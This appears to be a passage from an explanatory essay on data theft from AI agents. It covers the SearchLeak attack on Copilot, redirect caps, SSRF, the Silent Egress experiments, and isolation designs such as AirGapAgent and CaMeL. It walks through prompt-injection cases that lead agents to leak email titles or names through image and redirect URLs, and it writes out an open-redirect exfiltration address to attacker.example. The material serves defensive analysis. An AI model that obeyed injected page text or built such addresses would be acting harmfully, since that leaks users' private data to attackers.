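A rule in the fetch tool covers only requests that pass through that tool. An agent's answer can cause a request outside the tool if it contains an image address, because the program that displays the answer will load the image. The security company Varonis found a flaw of this kind, called SearchLeak, in Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise, which searches a company's emails, meetings and files for its employees. The Next Web reports that Microsoft assigned the flaw an official identifier on 4 June 2026 and rated it critical.

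*SearchLeak* (Taler, 2026) describes an attack that needed one click. The attacker sent an employee a link to Copilot's search page on a genuine Microsoft domain. The link filled the search box with text that Copilot treated as instructions. Copilot searched the employee's mailbox, took the title of an email and put it in the address of an image in its answer. Email titles often contain security codes, so a title alone could help an attacker get into another account.

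Microsoft had two safeguards against this. The first turned any active page elements in Copilot's answer into harmless text, but only once the answer was complete. By then the browser, which displayed the answer as it arrived, had already requested the image. The second was a Content Security Policy, a website's list of the domains from which the browser may load images and other material. The list excluded the attacker's domain but included Microsoft's search engine, Bing.

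Bing's search for similar pictures accepts the address of a picture, which Bing's server then fetches. The attacker's instructions had Copilot build a Bing address that contained the attacker's own address, which in turn contained the email's title. The browser sent the request to Bing, as the policy allowed. Bing's server then fetched the attacker's address, and the title appeared in the attacker's log. The policy could not prevent that fetch because it only governs the browser.

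Microsoft has fixed the flaw. Taler advises companies to treat any approved domain that fetches addresses on request as a possible route for leaking data. According to trackr.live, researchers had already exploited this weakness in 2025 with EchoLeak, an earlier attack on Copilot. It sent data out through a service that prepares link previews for Microsoft Teams and was also on the approved list.

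An exact-match rule would have caught the SearchLeak request. The complete Bing address contained the employee's email title and had never existed before, so no crawler could have recorded it and no earlier source could have supplied it. But the rule would have had to cover images in the browser as well as pages that Copilot opened. OpenAI applies its crawler rule to images, but Rehberger worries that some of its developers may not know about the rule and may build features without it, as happened with the earlier image check, which was missing from ChatGPT's Mac and iPhone apps.

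Companies can also inspect outgoing traffic for addresses nested inside other addresses, which is more useful than searching for scrambled text, according to trackr.live. SearchLeak's data was in plain words with underscores for spaces, so a filter for random-seeming strings would have missed it. However, the inspection logs may contain the security codes that the attacker wanted, and a company's equipment can't inspect a request that Bing makes from Microsoft's servers.

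Messaging apps send requests too. When someone posts a link in Slack or Telegram, the app may fetch the page to show a preview. *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps*, by the security company PromptArmor, explains that if an agent posts a link containing private data, the preview sends the data to the attacker before the user clicks anything. PromptArmor found that OpenClaw, a popular agent, was vulnerable to this in its default Telegram setup. Users can prevent it by setting `linkPreview` to `false`. Willison (2024) noted that Slack has a similar option for apps that post messages.

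A request can also come from the tools developers use to investigate attacks. In a case PromptArmor describes, a second model flagged an answer containing a malicious image, and the application withheld the answer from the user. A developer then opened the flagged conversation in OpenAI's log viewer, which displayed the image and so sent the user's data to the attacker.

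## Limits on redirects

An address rule applies before the agent's software sends a request, but a redirect comes afterwards. The server at an approved address replies that the page is somewhere else, and most software then requests the new address automatically. The model has no part in this and may receive no record of it. OpenAI gives redirects as one reason not to rely on lists of trusted sites. A link to a trusted domain can forward the visitor to an attacker's domain, and software that checks only the first domain will miss it.

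### How a redirect works

Under the IETF's *HTTP Semantics*, the internet standard for web requests, every reply has a three-digit status code whose first digit gives its class. Codes that start with 3 mean that the software must do something more to complete the request. For the common redirect codes (301, 302, 303, 307 and 308), it must request the address in the reply's `Location` header, a labelled line that precedes any content. Nielsen's *Fetch and 3xx Redirect Status Codes* gives the example of a browser that asks for an image, receives a 302 code with a new address, and downloads the image from there without the page's author having to do anything.

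The Fetch Standard, which the browser makers' standards group WHATWG maintains, specifies what a browser sends after each redirect code. Suppose an agent submits a form with a POST request. If the server replies with 301, 302 or 303, the browser switches to a GET request and drops the form's contents. If the server replies with 307 or 308, the browser sends the contents again to the new address, even if that address belongs to a different site. The browser removes the `Authorization` header, which can hold a password or access token, when a redirect leads to another origin.

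A page's own HTML or JavaScript can also make the browser load another address, for example after a few seconds. The server delivers such a page with status 200, which means success, so a simple HTTP client treats it as the final page and stops. A browser runs the page's code and loads the new address, so an agent that drives a real browser can end up on another site without any 3xx reply. A limit on 3xx replies won't prevent this, because the Fetch Standard counts redirects separately for each request and the page's code starts a new request.

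### Caps, checks and stops

People use "redirect limit" for several safeguards that block different things. A hop cap stops the software after a fixed number of redirects. A per-hop check applies the agent's address rule to each new address before the software requests it. A host-change stop lets the software follow redirects within one host but stops it when the next address is on a different host.

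Suppose a company's agent may contact only `news.example`. The news site has a page at `/go` that forwards visitors to whatever address follows it in the query string, perhaps so that the publisher can count clicks on outside links. Security engineers call this an open redirect. An attacker's text has reached the agent and misled the model into requesting this address:

`https://news.example/go?to=https://attacker.example/acme`

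The host is `news.example`, so the request passes the allowlist. The news site replies with a 302 redirect to `https://attacker.example/acme`. The software requests that address, and the name of the user's insurer, Acme, appears in the attacker's log.

The theft took one hop, so a cap of five would have permitted it. A per-hop check would have compared `attacker.example` with the allowlist and blocked the second request. This would have kept the insurer's name from the attacker, though the news site would still have received it.

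An open redirect can also bring an attacker's text into the agent's context. Even if a company limits its agent to a few trusted sites so that it reads only trustworthy pages, a forwarding page on one of those sites can send the agent to an attacker's page.

The table compares the safeguards on other redirect chains. The allowlist contains all of `news.example` and `docs.example`, but only the `/manuals` section of `files.example`, because customers can upload their own pages elsewhere on that site.

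| Chain of redirects | Cap of five hops | Allowlist check at every hop | Stop when the host changes |
|---|---|---|---|
| `news.example` to `attacker.example` | Permits | Blocks | Blocks |
| `news.example` to `docs.example` | Permits | Permits | Blocks |
| `files.example/manuals` to a customer's page on `files.example` | Permits | Blocks | Permits |
| Six hops within `news.example` | Blocks | Permits | Permits |
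| Two pages on `news.example` that redirect to each other forever | Blocks after five hops | Permits | Permits |

A cap of zero redirects would block every chain in the table, including the harmless ones. Websites use redirects to move visitors from unencrypted to encrypted addresses and to keep old links working after a reorganisation, so an agent that refused all redirects would often fail to open a page. Stopping at any change of host is less disruptive, but it would still block a redirect from `clinic.example` to `www.clinic.example`, two hosts that usually have the same owner.

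Repeating the address check at each redirect usually adds more protection under an allowlist than under a URL provenance rule. Under an allowlist, a single open redirect can carry as much data as the address will hold. Under a provenance rule, the model can't write the forwarding address itself, so a redirect usually reveals no more than the model's choice of link already did.

An agent that uses its user's logins is an exception. The website can identify the user and put private values into the `Location` header. Many login systems do this when they send a visitor back to the original site with a one-time code in the address. If a flaw in the login system sends that code to the wrong host, the secret leaks even though neither the model nor the first address contained it. *URLs of intermediary redirects are leakable in practice (same-origin)*, a bug report on the Fetch Standard by ukusormus,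 quotes one of the standard's authors, who considers a `Location` header about as sensitive as an HttpOnly cookie. Browsers hide such cookies from the code on a page, often because they keep the user logged in.

### Why browsers allow twenty hops

The usual redirect caps began as a way to stop loops. An early version of HTTP/1.1 advised software not to follow more than five redirects automatically, because longer chains "usually indicate an infinite loop". Gettys, an author of that version, later circulated replacement wording that dropped the number and called for loop detection, since each redirect in a loop generates network traffic. Under the current standard, clients should detect cyclical redirections and intervene, and the limit of five is mentioned only as history. Fielding (2024), one of the standard's editors, quoted this passage when he rejected a proposed correction.

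Under the Fetch Standard, a browser follows up to 20 redirects and returns an error at the next one. Dumez (2017) asked why the limit was 20 and whether it could be lowered. Chrome and Firefox already used that number, but Apple's networking library, CFNetwork, had a fixed limit of 16, so software built on it couldn't comply. His concern was compatibility, and either limit still lets an attacker chain many redirects.

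A small cap on redirects saves an agent time and limits how many servers one tool call can contact. But it can't distinguish a clinic that has moved its website from an open redirect that sends data to a thief, since both need only one hop. It also doesn't hinder theft by link-following, as in the attack on Claude's memories, because each new fetch starts with a redirect count of zero.

### Redirects into a private network

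An attacker can also use a redirect to reach a server closed to the public. Companies run databases, control panels and test sites that accept requests only from inside their own network. *Server Side Request Forgery (SSRF)*, a page in MDN's reference for web developers, describes a website that fetches an image from any address a visitor gives it. If the website's server can reach the company's internal network, a visitor can give it an internal address and read what comes back. This is server-side request forgery, in which an attacker makes someone else's server send a request that the attacker could not usefully send directly.

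OWASP, a foundation that publishes security guidance, added server-side request forgery to its list of the ten main risks to web applications in 2021. According to OWASP's *Server-Side Request Forgery (SSRF)* (2021), the flaw came first in a survey of practitioners even though testing found it in relatively few applications, with an average incidence of 2.72%. Part of the worry is that many servers behind the firewall run local services that don't require a password, because their owners assume that only the same machine can reach them (OWASP, 2024).

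A web fetch tool has the same basic design as MDN's image fetcher. It takes an address that somebody else may have influenced and requests it from the machine it runs on. If that is the user's work computer, the tool may be able to reach the employer's internal servers. An attacker might put a link to an internal address on a web page. If the tool refuses internal addresses, the attacker can link to a public address that redirects to an internal one.

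*Lab 05*, by 4ykh4ncyb3r, solves and explains a training exercise in which one open redirect is enough to bypass an allowlist. An online shop's stock checker will fetch only addresses on the shop's own domain, but the shop's "next product" button uses an open redirect on that domain. The attacker gives the stock checker the address of the open redirect, with an internal address inside it. The stock checker accepts the shop's domain, receives a 302 reply and follows it to the internal server.

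Cornucopia's *Server-Side Request Forgery (SSRF)* reproduces OWASP's advice, which includes disabling HTTP redirects, restricting the scheme, port and destination to an approved list, and not sending raw responses to the requester. This works well for a stock checker, which contacts only a few known addresses. A browsing agent needs redirects and can't list every public site in advance, so its developers have to refuse private destinations at every hop instead.

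OWASP warns against lists of forbidden addresses and pattern matching, because attackers have collections of ways around them. For instance, many programs accept `127.0.0.1`, the address a computer uses for itself, written as one long number, which a search for the familiar text would miss. A developer can avoid much of this problem by checking the numeric address the software is about to connect to, in a standard form, instead of the URL's text. The software can compare that address with the ranges reserved for private networks, which are published and finite.

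The timing of the check also matters. Software looks up a domain name such as `clinic.example` to find its numeric address when it needs to connect, and that address can change between lookups. An attacker who controls the domain can give a harmless public address when the tool checks the name and an internal address a moment later when it connects. OWASP mentions this attack, called DNS rebinding, along with others that exploit the gap between checking something and using it. The tool can prevent it by looking up the name once, checking the resulting address and connecting to exactly that address. It has to repeat this for every redirect, because each one may name a new domain.

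An agent passes the fetched page to its model, which may read an internal document and then follow an instruction to send it elsewhere. Restricting outgoing addresses helps even after a redirect has bypassed the check on internal addresses, because the attacker still needs a way to get the document out.

### What agent tools do

Some developers already limit the number of redirects and check each one. A web tool hosted by LM Studio, for models that run on a user's own computer, follows at most ten redirects by default and repeats its check for server-side request forgery at each one. Another agent's fetch tool, whose source code is in Docs.rs' *oy-cli 0.10.6*, also stops after ten. Before each redirect, it checks that the new address has a host and uses HTTP or HTTPS.

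Both tools can do this because their own code handles each reply. A tool built as a script inside a web page can't, because under the Fetch Standard browsers hide the intermediate addresses from scripts to protect any private values in them. The script can have the browser follow the whole chain, treat any redirect as an error, or return a reply with its details hidden. If the browser follows the chain, the script can read the final address afterwards, but by then the attacker's server has received the request. A developer of such a tool who needs to enforce an allowlist should refuse all redirects or fetch pages through a separate server that can check each hop.

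Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, fetches web pages with a tool called WebFetch. Shilkov (2025), in *Inside Claude Code's Web Tools*, observed the program as it ran and found that WebFetch automatically followed redirects within the same host. When a redirect led to another host, the tool returned the details to the model, which had to make another tool call to continue.

Anthropic's documentation confirms the stop. WebFetch returns a text result naming the original address and the redirect's target, and "Claude then fetches the new URL with a second WebFetch call." The documentation doesn't suggest that Claude considers whether to continue. If a malicious page has already misled Claude into opening the first address, Claude has little reason to refuse the next one. The attacker also chooses the target address and can put persuasive words in it. WebFetch normally has a separate model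 call extract what Claude needs from a page, but the redirect notice seems to reach Claude without that step.

The stop is useful mainly because the second call goes through Claude Code's permission rules again, so the user's settings determine who decides whether to allow it. In Manual and acceptEdits modes, the program asks the user before fetching from a new domain, unless the user's rules already cover that domain or it belongs to a built-in set of documentation sites. A user who has permanently approved `news.example` would still be asked about `attacker.example`. In auto mode, a classifier makes most of these decisions. In bypassPermissions mode, the program doesn't ask unless the user has written a rule requiring it to ask about that domain, so the decision is largely Claude's.

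A user can also avoid the approval prompt by allowing every domain with a single rule, `WebFetch(domain:*)`. Anthropic still runs a domain safety check before each fetch unless a setting turns it off. Shilkov found that Claude Code sent the domain's name to an Anthropic server, which returned whether fetching from that domain was allowed. He couldn't see how the server classified domains, but guessed that it used a list of obviously malicious ones. If so, the check would probably miss a domain that an attacker had just registered.

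WebFetch also refuses `localhost`, which refers to the computer itself, and any hostname without a dot, such as a bare intranet name. This rule doesn't block numeric addresses, which contain dots, or the full dotted names that many companies give their internal servers. The error message includes an instruction for Claude to reach local servers with `curl`, a command-line download program, through its Bash tool. This is reasonable because developers often need to open a test site on their own machine, but `curl` has its own redirect behaviour, and WebFetch's host-change stop doesn't apply to it.

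Anthropic's separate fetch tool for developers, which has the `allowed_domains` setting, is harder to assess. Its documentation lists eight error codes, including one for an address that the domain rules block, but none specifically for a redirect. A developer who relies on the allowlist should test whether the tool follows a redirect from a listed domain to an unlisted one.

### The Silent Egress experiments

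*Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026), a study from eBay, seems to be the most directly relevant to redirect limits. Its experiments don't support its claim that "redirect-chain analysis" was among the considerably more effective defences against data theft by web pages.

The researchers built an agent that automatically previewed any web page a user mentioned and could send web requests. It ran on qwen2.5:7b, which has about 7 billion parameters and is small by current standards. They put sensitive data directly in the context and gave the model only minimal standing instructions on how to call the tool. The user always asked for a summary of the page. The page contained an instruction, presented as a routine technical requirement, to send the data to the attacker's server.

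The experiment varied where the instruction appeared on the page (title, metadata description, body or link text), whether the agent received the page directly or through up to three redirects, and whether the instruction asked for the data in one request or split across four. There were 30 runs of each of the 16 combinations, or 480 in all.

The agent contacted the attacker's server in 423 of 480 runs (88.1%). The rate was 0.88 when the agent received the page directly and 0.89 when the page came through redirects (210 and 213 of 240 runs, calculated from the results for each combination). In 120 further runs with harmless pages, the agent never contacted the server. In 95% of the successful attacks, the user saw a harmless-looking answer, so a safety test that examined only answers would have missed nearly all of these attacks.

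The similar rates aren't surprising, because the redirects came before the attack and only brought the agent to the malicious page. Once the page's text was in the context, the model read the same words whether or not the agent had been redirected. The agent then sent the data directly to the attacker. The experiment shows that redirects didn't hinder an injection, but it didn't test whether a redirect could carry data past an allowlist. A cap of five hops would have made no difference, since no chain had more than three.

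Splitting the data made the attack less reliable. The agent contacted the attacker in about 99% of runs with a single request and 77% of runs with split requests. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model lost track of the longer instructions. However, each split request contained only a short fragment, which a filter looking for a complete key would probably miss.

It is unclear how much of the secret arrived this way. The paper's measure of early leakage, the share of runs in which sensitive data appeared in the first request, fell from 0.967 to 0.263 when the agent split the data. The paper gives 0.158 for the first three requests, which can't be right under its definition, because any run with a leak in the first request also has a leak in the first three. The paper also defines a completion rate, the share of runs in which all the fragments arrived, but reports no value for it. The study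 therefore shows that a small model will attempt a split transfer, but not how often the attacker could have reassembled the secret.

The researchers compared the defences using one combination: an instruction in the page's body, direct delivery and a single request. They ran each defence 30 times. The table gives their percentages as numbers of runs.

| Defence | Runs in which the agent tried to contact the attacker | Runs in which it succeeded |
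|---|---|---|
| None | 30 | 30 |
| Standing instruction never to obey web content | 20 | 20 |
| Tags that mark web content as untrusted | 30 | 30 |
| Both of these | 17 | 17 |
| Domain allowlist | 30 | 0 |
| "Redirect detection" | 25 | 0 |
| Filter for words such as "password" in addresses | 7 | 0 |
| Filter for random-looking text in addresses | 0 | 0 |
| All defences together | 0 | 0 |

No run in this comparison involved a redirect, and the defence called "redirect detection" didn't examine redirects. It blocked numeric addresses, eight domain endings that the researchers considered suspicious (such as `.xyz`), and paths containing the words "exfil", "collect", "steal", "leak" or "dump". The attacker's domain, `evil-collector.net`, isn't numeric and doesn't have one of those endings, so the filter probably worked because the attack used the path `/collect`. An attacker could get past it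 by changing the path to `/hours`.

The results for the two content filters are also hard to interpret. The agent tried to contact the attacker in every run without a defence, but in none with the random-text filter on. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoids random text when monitoring is active, but the filter they describe inspects addresses, and they don't explain how the model would know about it. Since the filter had nothing to block, its perfect score isn't evidence that it works. They say the word filter was triggered in only seven runs because the model sometimes disguised the data, but disguised data should then have got through, and they report that none did.

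The allowlist result is more reliable but less informative, because the researchers chose a domain clearly outside the list, and code that compares each host with the list will always block such a domain. Still, the agent kept trying to reach it in all 30 runs and the allowlist blocked it each time, whereas the best combination of written warnings failed in 17. This supports enforcing address rules in code, at least for a model this easy to mislead.

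The leak rates don't transfer to commercial agents. Lan and colleagues acknowledge that they set up the test to favour the attacker. They call their rates a lower bound because they used simple attack instructions and a cleverer attacker might do better. But the rates aren't a lower bound for better-defended systems, because the sensitive data in plain view and the minimal standing instructions both push them up. Lan and colleagues also argue that more capable models might be easier to exploit because such models follow instructions more faithfully, but they tested only one model.

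Lan and colleagues warn in their discussion that attackers can get around an allowlist through open redirects on trusted sites, and they recommend also analyzing the whole redirect chain. This is sound advice, and the `news.example` case shows why it should work, but they did not test it. A test would put an open redirect on one of the listed domains and compare an agent that checks only the first address with one that checks every hop.

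## Keeping private information away from the part that browses

Context isolation keeps private information out of the model or session that reads untrusted pages or writes outbound requests. This limits what a misled agent can send, whereas rules on addresses and redirects limit where it can send information. If the fake coffee shop's notice had reached a model without Paul's memories, that model would have had no name to spell out, even if the notice had misled it.

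Complete isolation is impossible for most errands, because the request itself reveals something. Suppose a woman in Denver who has epilepsy asks her agent to "find a clinic near me that treats my condition". Before a search engine can answer, some part of the system has to replace "near me" and "my condition" with facts from her notes and send them to the search provider. Designers have to decide which facts to send and which part of the system chooses them.

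### What the search has to reveal

The woman's notes also contain her street address, phone number, insurer, employer and recent divorce. The table shows who would need each fact.

| Fact | Search provider | Clinic's website, while the agent reads it | Clinic, when she books | What she loses if the agent withholds it |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Epilepsy | Needed, though "neurology" might do | Revealed if the agent opens the epilepsy page | Needed | The right kind of clinic |
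| Denver, or a part of it | Needed | Not needed | Not needed | Nearby results |
| Street address | Not needed | Not needed | Perhaps, to register her | Exact travel times |
| Insurer | Not needed if clinics list the insurers they accept | Not needed | Needed | Some time, because the agent has to check more clinics |
| Name and phone number | Not needed | Not needed | Needed | The booking |
| Employer and divorce | Not needed | Not needed | Not needed | Nothing |

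It can be proper to tell one party a fact and improper to tell another. *AirGapAgent* (Bagdasarian, Kairouz and colleagues, 2024) builds on contextual integrity, a theory developed by the philosopher Helen Nissenbaum that defines privacy as the appropriate flow of information. Whether a flow is appropriate depends on who sends the information, who receives it, whom it concerns, what type it is, and the terms on which it is shared. A patient tells a clinic their diagnosis on the understanding that the clinic will keep it confidential, so that disclosure is proper, but a coffee shop has no claim to the same information. The search provider needs some version of the diagnosis but receives it on different terms, which is a reason to send "neurology" rather than the diagnosis itself if the results are good enough.

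The theory needs norms for each setting, and people disagree about them. Bagdasarian and colleagues had a language model, Gemini Ultra, label 26 kinds of personal fact as proper or improper to share in eight tasks, and then checked the labels by hand. A home address is labeled improper to share in all eight tasks, including a doctor's appointment. Holiday preferences are labeled proper to share at a job interview, on the grounds that an employer has to schedule shifts. An agent that followed the rule on addresses could search near the woman's home only if it could share the city without the street.

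### Telling the agent not to share

In the weakest form of isolation, the developer keeps everything in one context and instructs the agent to reveal only what the task needs. This doesn't separate private information from browsing, but it does reduce how often agents disclose unnecessary details, a common problem even when nobody is attacking them.

*AgentDAM* (Zharmagambetov, Pavlova and colleagues, 2025) tested whether agents reveal private information irrelevant to their task, using 246 tasks on working copies of a shopping site, a discussion forum and GitLab, a site for software projects. Each task came with a chat, email thread or set of notes that mixed relevant facts with irrelevant private ones. For example, an agent might have to comment on a colleague's code using a conversation that also mentioned somebody's upcoming absence. A second model checked whether the agent typed any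 of the irrelevant private facts. The researchers then repeated the tests with instructions that explained what counts as sensitive and gave worked examples.

| Model | Tasks with a leak | With privacy instructions | Tasks completed | With privacy instructions |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 36% | 9% | 46% | 42% |
| GPT-4o-mini | 46% | 18% | 34% | 32% |
| GPT-4-turbo | 25% | 11% | 48% | 42% |
| Llama 3.2 90B | 12% | 8% | 33% | 30% |
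| Llama 3.3 70B | 12% | 6% | 40% | 39% |
| Claude 3.5 Sonnet | 10% | 7% | 35% | 31% |

With the instructions, the number of tasks in which at least one model leaked something fell from 162 to 73, out of 246. Tasks that involved writing forum posts accounted for 71 of that 89-task drop. For contact forms, which are closer to what a clinic would ask the woman to fill in, the number fell only from 22 to 16, out of 42.

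The paper also warns that asking a model about privacy overstates how well it will behave. This conclusion is less reliable than it looks because the comparison seems to use the wrong numbers. The figures given for the agents' privacy are identical to their task completion rates. Against the paper's actual privacy scores, the warning holds for GPT-4o and GPT-4o-mini but not for the two Llama models, which did better in practice than in their answers. GPT-4o-mini withheld private facts in 89% of cases when asked and 54% in practice.

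All of these models date from 2024 or earlier, but newer ones also overshare. *GapLeak* (Cheong, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) tested six models, including Claude Sonnet 4.6 and GPT 5.4, on job applications, product returns, travel bookings and medical intake forms. The user gave the agent a summary that lacked one fact the form required, such as an insurance number. That fact was in files or account pages that the agent could open but the user hadn't offered. The agents often searched for it rather than leaving the field blank, and picked up other sensitive details on the way. When the form then invited them to add "helpful" extra information, they pasted in some of what they had found, without any instruction to abandon the task.

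Cheong and colleagues put the average rate of unauthorised disclosure at about 37%, using a strict definition that counts every optional field as unauthorised. On the medical form, the agents gave relatives' contact details in nearly every completed run, even when the website did nothing to encourage it, but many patients would consider an emergency contact appropriate there. More worryingly, disclosures still occurred in 77% of completed tasks when the instructions named the sources the agent could open and told it to leave other fields blank, and the share of tasks completed fell to 30%.

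In *SPILLage*, Roh, Bagdasarian and colleagues (2026) found that privacy instructions did not stop agents from oversharing on live shopping sites and sometimes made it worse. The survey *Agents That Know Too Much* (2026) found that no benchmark yet tests an agent's queries, memory and messages together under a single privacy policy, so these studies can't be combined into one leak rate.

### Removing details before they leave

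Software can also edit the text, either before the agent receives it or before a query or form goes out. In *Protecting Users From Themselves*, Ngong, Kadhe and colleagues propose a layer between the user and the assistant that rewrites prompts so that users disclose only what is relevant to their request. In their user study, even people who considered themselves careful gave away sensitive facts indirectly. In the clinic search, such a layer could turn a rambling message about a divorce and a change of insurer into "epilepsy clinic in Denver".

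Zharmagambetov and colleagues tried this by having GPT-4o strip irrelevant details from the user's material before the task began. They call the method ineffective, which seems harsh. With GPT-4o as the agent, leaks fell from 36% of tasks to 14%, while the share of tasks completed fell only from 46% to 43%. The privacy instructions reduced leaks further, to 9%, but the agent completed slightly fewer tasks.

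If the software removes private details before they reach the model, a malicious page can't get the model to reveal them. An instruction to keep the details private is weaker because text on the page may persuade the model to ignore it. Editing outgoing text is also weaker because the details are still in the context, and an attacker can use the page to get the model to send them in a form the editor won't recognise.

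Editing also misses what an agent reveals by clicking. Roh and colleagues give the example of a recently divorced user with diabetes who wants glucose test strips. The agent may type nothing about the divorce but click on a category for divorce parties. In 1,080 runs on Amazon and eBay, disclosures through clicks, scrolling and similar behaviour outnumbered disclosures in text by five to one. This ratio may be too high, because the model that judged the runs was given the user's prompt and the agent's stated next goal, neither of which the shop would see. But shops log clicks, and *Actions Speak Louder than Words* (2026) points out that an agent's choice of pages can depend on attributes and preferences gathered over many conversations. If the woman's notes mention a wheelchair, the agent may open the accessibility page on every clinic's site.

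Several queries that are harmless on their own can also reveal private information together. In *MosaicLeaks*, Laradji, Taslakian and Pardinas (2026) built 1,001 research tasks in which an agent had to combine a company's private documents with web searches. A second model that saw only the searches could often work out the company's secrets, even when no single query revealed much. In the woman's case, an editor that examines each query separately would pass a search for neurologists in Denver, another for clinics that accept her insurer and a third for parking near her office, even though the three together could point to one person.

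Laradji and colleagues found that training an agent only to complete its tasks made the leaks worse, so they also rewarded it for low leakage, as judged by a classifier that considered each query and the whole series. This teaches the agent to avoid disclosure, but the protection still depends on a model's judgement.

Cheong and colleagues had more success checking each form field just before submission, which removed over 96% of the unauthorised disclosures without lowering task completion further. The check suits forms because the software can identify exactly what is about to be sent and who will receive it. It wouldn't have stopped Paul's attack, because Claude submitted no form.

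### Choosing the facts before the conversation starts

AirGapAgent moves the decision to a point where no outsider can influence it. It works as follows:

1. The user states the task and whom the agent will deal with.
2. One model, the minimiser, reads the task and all the user's stored facts, and selects those that are appropriate to share. It has seen nothing from the outside party.
3. A second model receives only the selected facts and conducts the conversation.
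4. If the outside party asks for anything else, the second model doesn't have it. The system can ask the user, who may approve that one fact.

For the clinic search, the minimiser might select only "epilepsy" and "Denver". A page could then claim that the law requires visitors to name their employer, but the model reading it couldn't reveal the user's employer because it was never given that information.

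Bagdasarian and colleagues tested the design against what they call context hijacking, in which the outside party invents a situation where disclosing the information would be appropriate. In their example, a restaurant's booking system sends a message that aliens have invaded and humanity's survival depends on the customer's age. Paul's notice in Cloudflare's name worked in a similar way, but its story was more plausible. The table compares AirGapAgent with a single model that had all the facts and was instructed to protect them.

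| Model | Private facts protected under attack: single model | AirGapAgent | Appropriate facts shared without an attack: single model | AirGapAgent |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini Ultra | 45% | 97% | 99% | 89% |
| Gemini Pro | 38% | 92% | 74% | 66% |
| GPT-4 | 31% | 87% | 80% | 79% |
| Mistral Large | 35% | 91% | 87% | 83% |

The right-hand columns show results for single questions, so they probably understate how much AirGapAgent would reduce task completion. If a booking needed five facts and Gemini Ultra's errors were independent, AirGapAgent would have all five about 55% of the time, compared with 95% for the single model. Asking the user for missing facts would narrow the gap somewhat.

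The minimiser also needs a clear task. When Bagdasarian and colleagues gave it only the general area, such as health or scheduling, average protection fell from 97% to 69%, even without an attack. "Find a clinic near me that treats my condition" is specific enough to guide which facts it shares, but "deal with my health admin" probably isn't.

A more serious limit is the assumption that everything in the user's store is trustworthy. That was true in the experiments, where the store was a list of 26 labelled facts. A real mailbox contains messages from strangers, and the resignation letter attack on ChatGPT Atlas began with one. If the minimiser reads such a message while deciding what to share, the attacker can influence the decision.

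### Browsing without memory or accounts

A developer can keep private information out of the browsing session instead of relying on a model to choose which facts to share. After a year of running a commercial browser agent, Vardanyan (2025) argues in *Building Browser Agents* for limits of this general kind, enforced by code.

Memory, mail and logins are separate sources of private information, so switching one off leaves the others accessible. For tasks that don't need an account, OpenAI recommends the ChatGPT Atlas agent's logged-out mode, which visits sites without the user's existing logins. Brave, a browser maker, separates logins by default. The AI browsing feature it released for testing in December 2025 ran in its own browser profile, with cookies and other storage separate from the user's. Claude in Chrome instead works inside the user's logged-in browser.

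Logging out keeps an agent away from the user's inbox and bank account, but it wouldn't have protected Paul, whose details came from Claude's memory.

OpenAI's Lockdown Mode, introduced in February 2026 for users at unusually high risk, also restricts requests by letting ChatGPT read only cached copies of web pages, so no live request reaches the site. This resembles the trusted third party that Zenity Labs recommends and has the same drawback for live information.

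Anthropic's main method is to confine the programs that Claude runs. The company's article *How we contain Claude across products* explains that "if credentials never enter the sandbox, they can't be exfiltrated" (quoted in Willison, 2026). A sandbox is a closed environment that restricts which files and servers a program can reach. Claude.ai uses one called gVisor, Claude Code uses tools built for macOS and Linux, and Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, runs in a full virtual machine.

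The principle is sound, and it applies to memories as well as passwords. But Anthropic published this account in May 2026, two months before Paul's post, and sandboxing the programs doesn't protect information in the model's context.

With memory and accounts off, the woman has to type "epilepsy clinic in Denver" herself. A malicious page could still learn those two facts from her request, but nothing else about her. The drawback is that the agent can't check her calendar, apply her insurer's rules or book through her account at a clinic she already uses.

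### A reader with no secrets and no tools

A developer can keep the notes available by splitting the work between two models. Willison proposed this pattern in 2023. A privileged model has the user's request, the notes and the tools, but never reads untrusted text. A quarantined model reads the untrusted text and has neither private information nor tools. Ordinary code passes material between them.

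For the clinic search, the privileged model uses the woman's notes to write the query "epilepsy clinic Denver". The code runs the search, fetches the pages and has the quarantined model extract each clinic's name, phone number and accepted insurers. The code stores the results under labels such as `clinic_1`. The privileged model can have the code display `clinic_1` without reading its contents itself. Malicious instructions on a page reach only the quarantined model, which can return a false phone number but can't look up the woman's employer or send a message.

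This protection depends on keeping the quarantined model's free text away from the privileged model. If the privileged model reads a summary of the page, the summary can include instructions hidden in the page. Developers can reduce the risk by having the code accept only narrow answers, such as a phone number in the right format or an insurer from a fixed list. The name of the woman's insurer can then stay on the private side, where code compares it with each clinic's list.

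This separation makes the agent less flexible, because the privileged model has to choose questions about pages it can't see. If a clinic's page has a notice that the epilepsy service has moved to another hospital, but none of the questions cover moves, the quarantined model has no field to report it in.

### A plan fixed before any page is read

Even with two models, a page can influence what the agent does next if the privileged model waits for the results of one step before choosing another. CaMeL, a design that Google DeepMind published in 2025, fixes the steps in advance. The privileged model reads only the user's request and writes a short program for the whole task. For the clinic search, the program might run one query, open the first ten results, have the quarantined model extract the same details from each, discard clinics that don't accept the insurer and show the rest. An interpreter,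 which is ordinary code, then runs the program. No page can add a step that reads the woman's email, because the program was complete before the first page arrived.

A fixed plan still leaves an attacker some influence. If the program sends an enquiry to whatever email address the clinic's page gives, an attacker who can change the page can choose where the enquiry goes. CaMeL's interpreter therefore also tracks where each value came from and who may receive it, and checks this before each tool call.

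On AgentDojo, a test suite of office tasks with planted injections, CaMeL completed 77% of tasks with its security guarantees in place, compared with 84% for an undefended agent, according to the revised version of the CaMeL paper. That is a small loss for protection that doesn't depend on a model noticing an attack. But AgentDojo's tasks mostly use known tools for email, banking, messaging and travel, so a model can plan how to use them in advance. Booking on an unfamiliar clinic's site may involve a choice of branch, a questionnaire and a calendar that the model couldn't have foreseen. CaMeL also doesn't check whether the information on a page is true, so a fake clinic can still appear in the results.

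In many agents, the planner can change the plan during the task. Kim and colleagues describe how developers can assign planning and acting to separate models, which allows finer security boundaries between them. In Agent-E, an open-source web agent, a planner model writes a list of steps and another model carries them out in the browser, but the planner reviews progress after every step and may revise the list.

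In *Context manipulation attacks*, Patlan, Hebbar and colleagues (2025) attacked Agent-E by altering its stored plan. The planner usually rejected a step unrelated to the user's request, such as sending an address to a stranger during a recipe search. It accepted the harmful step more often when related steps led up to it, as in a plan to find restaurants that serve the dish, look up the user's address to see which is closest, and then send the address to the attacker's site. Attacks that altered the plan succeeded up to three times as often as comparable injections through web pages.

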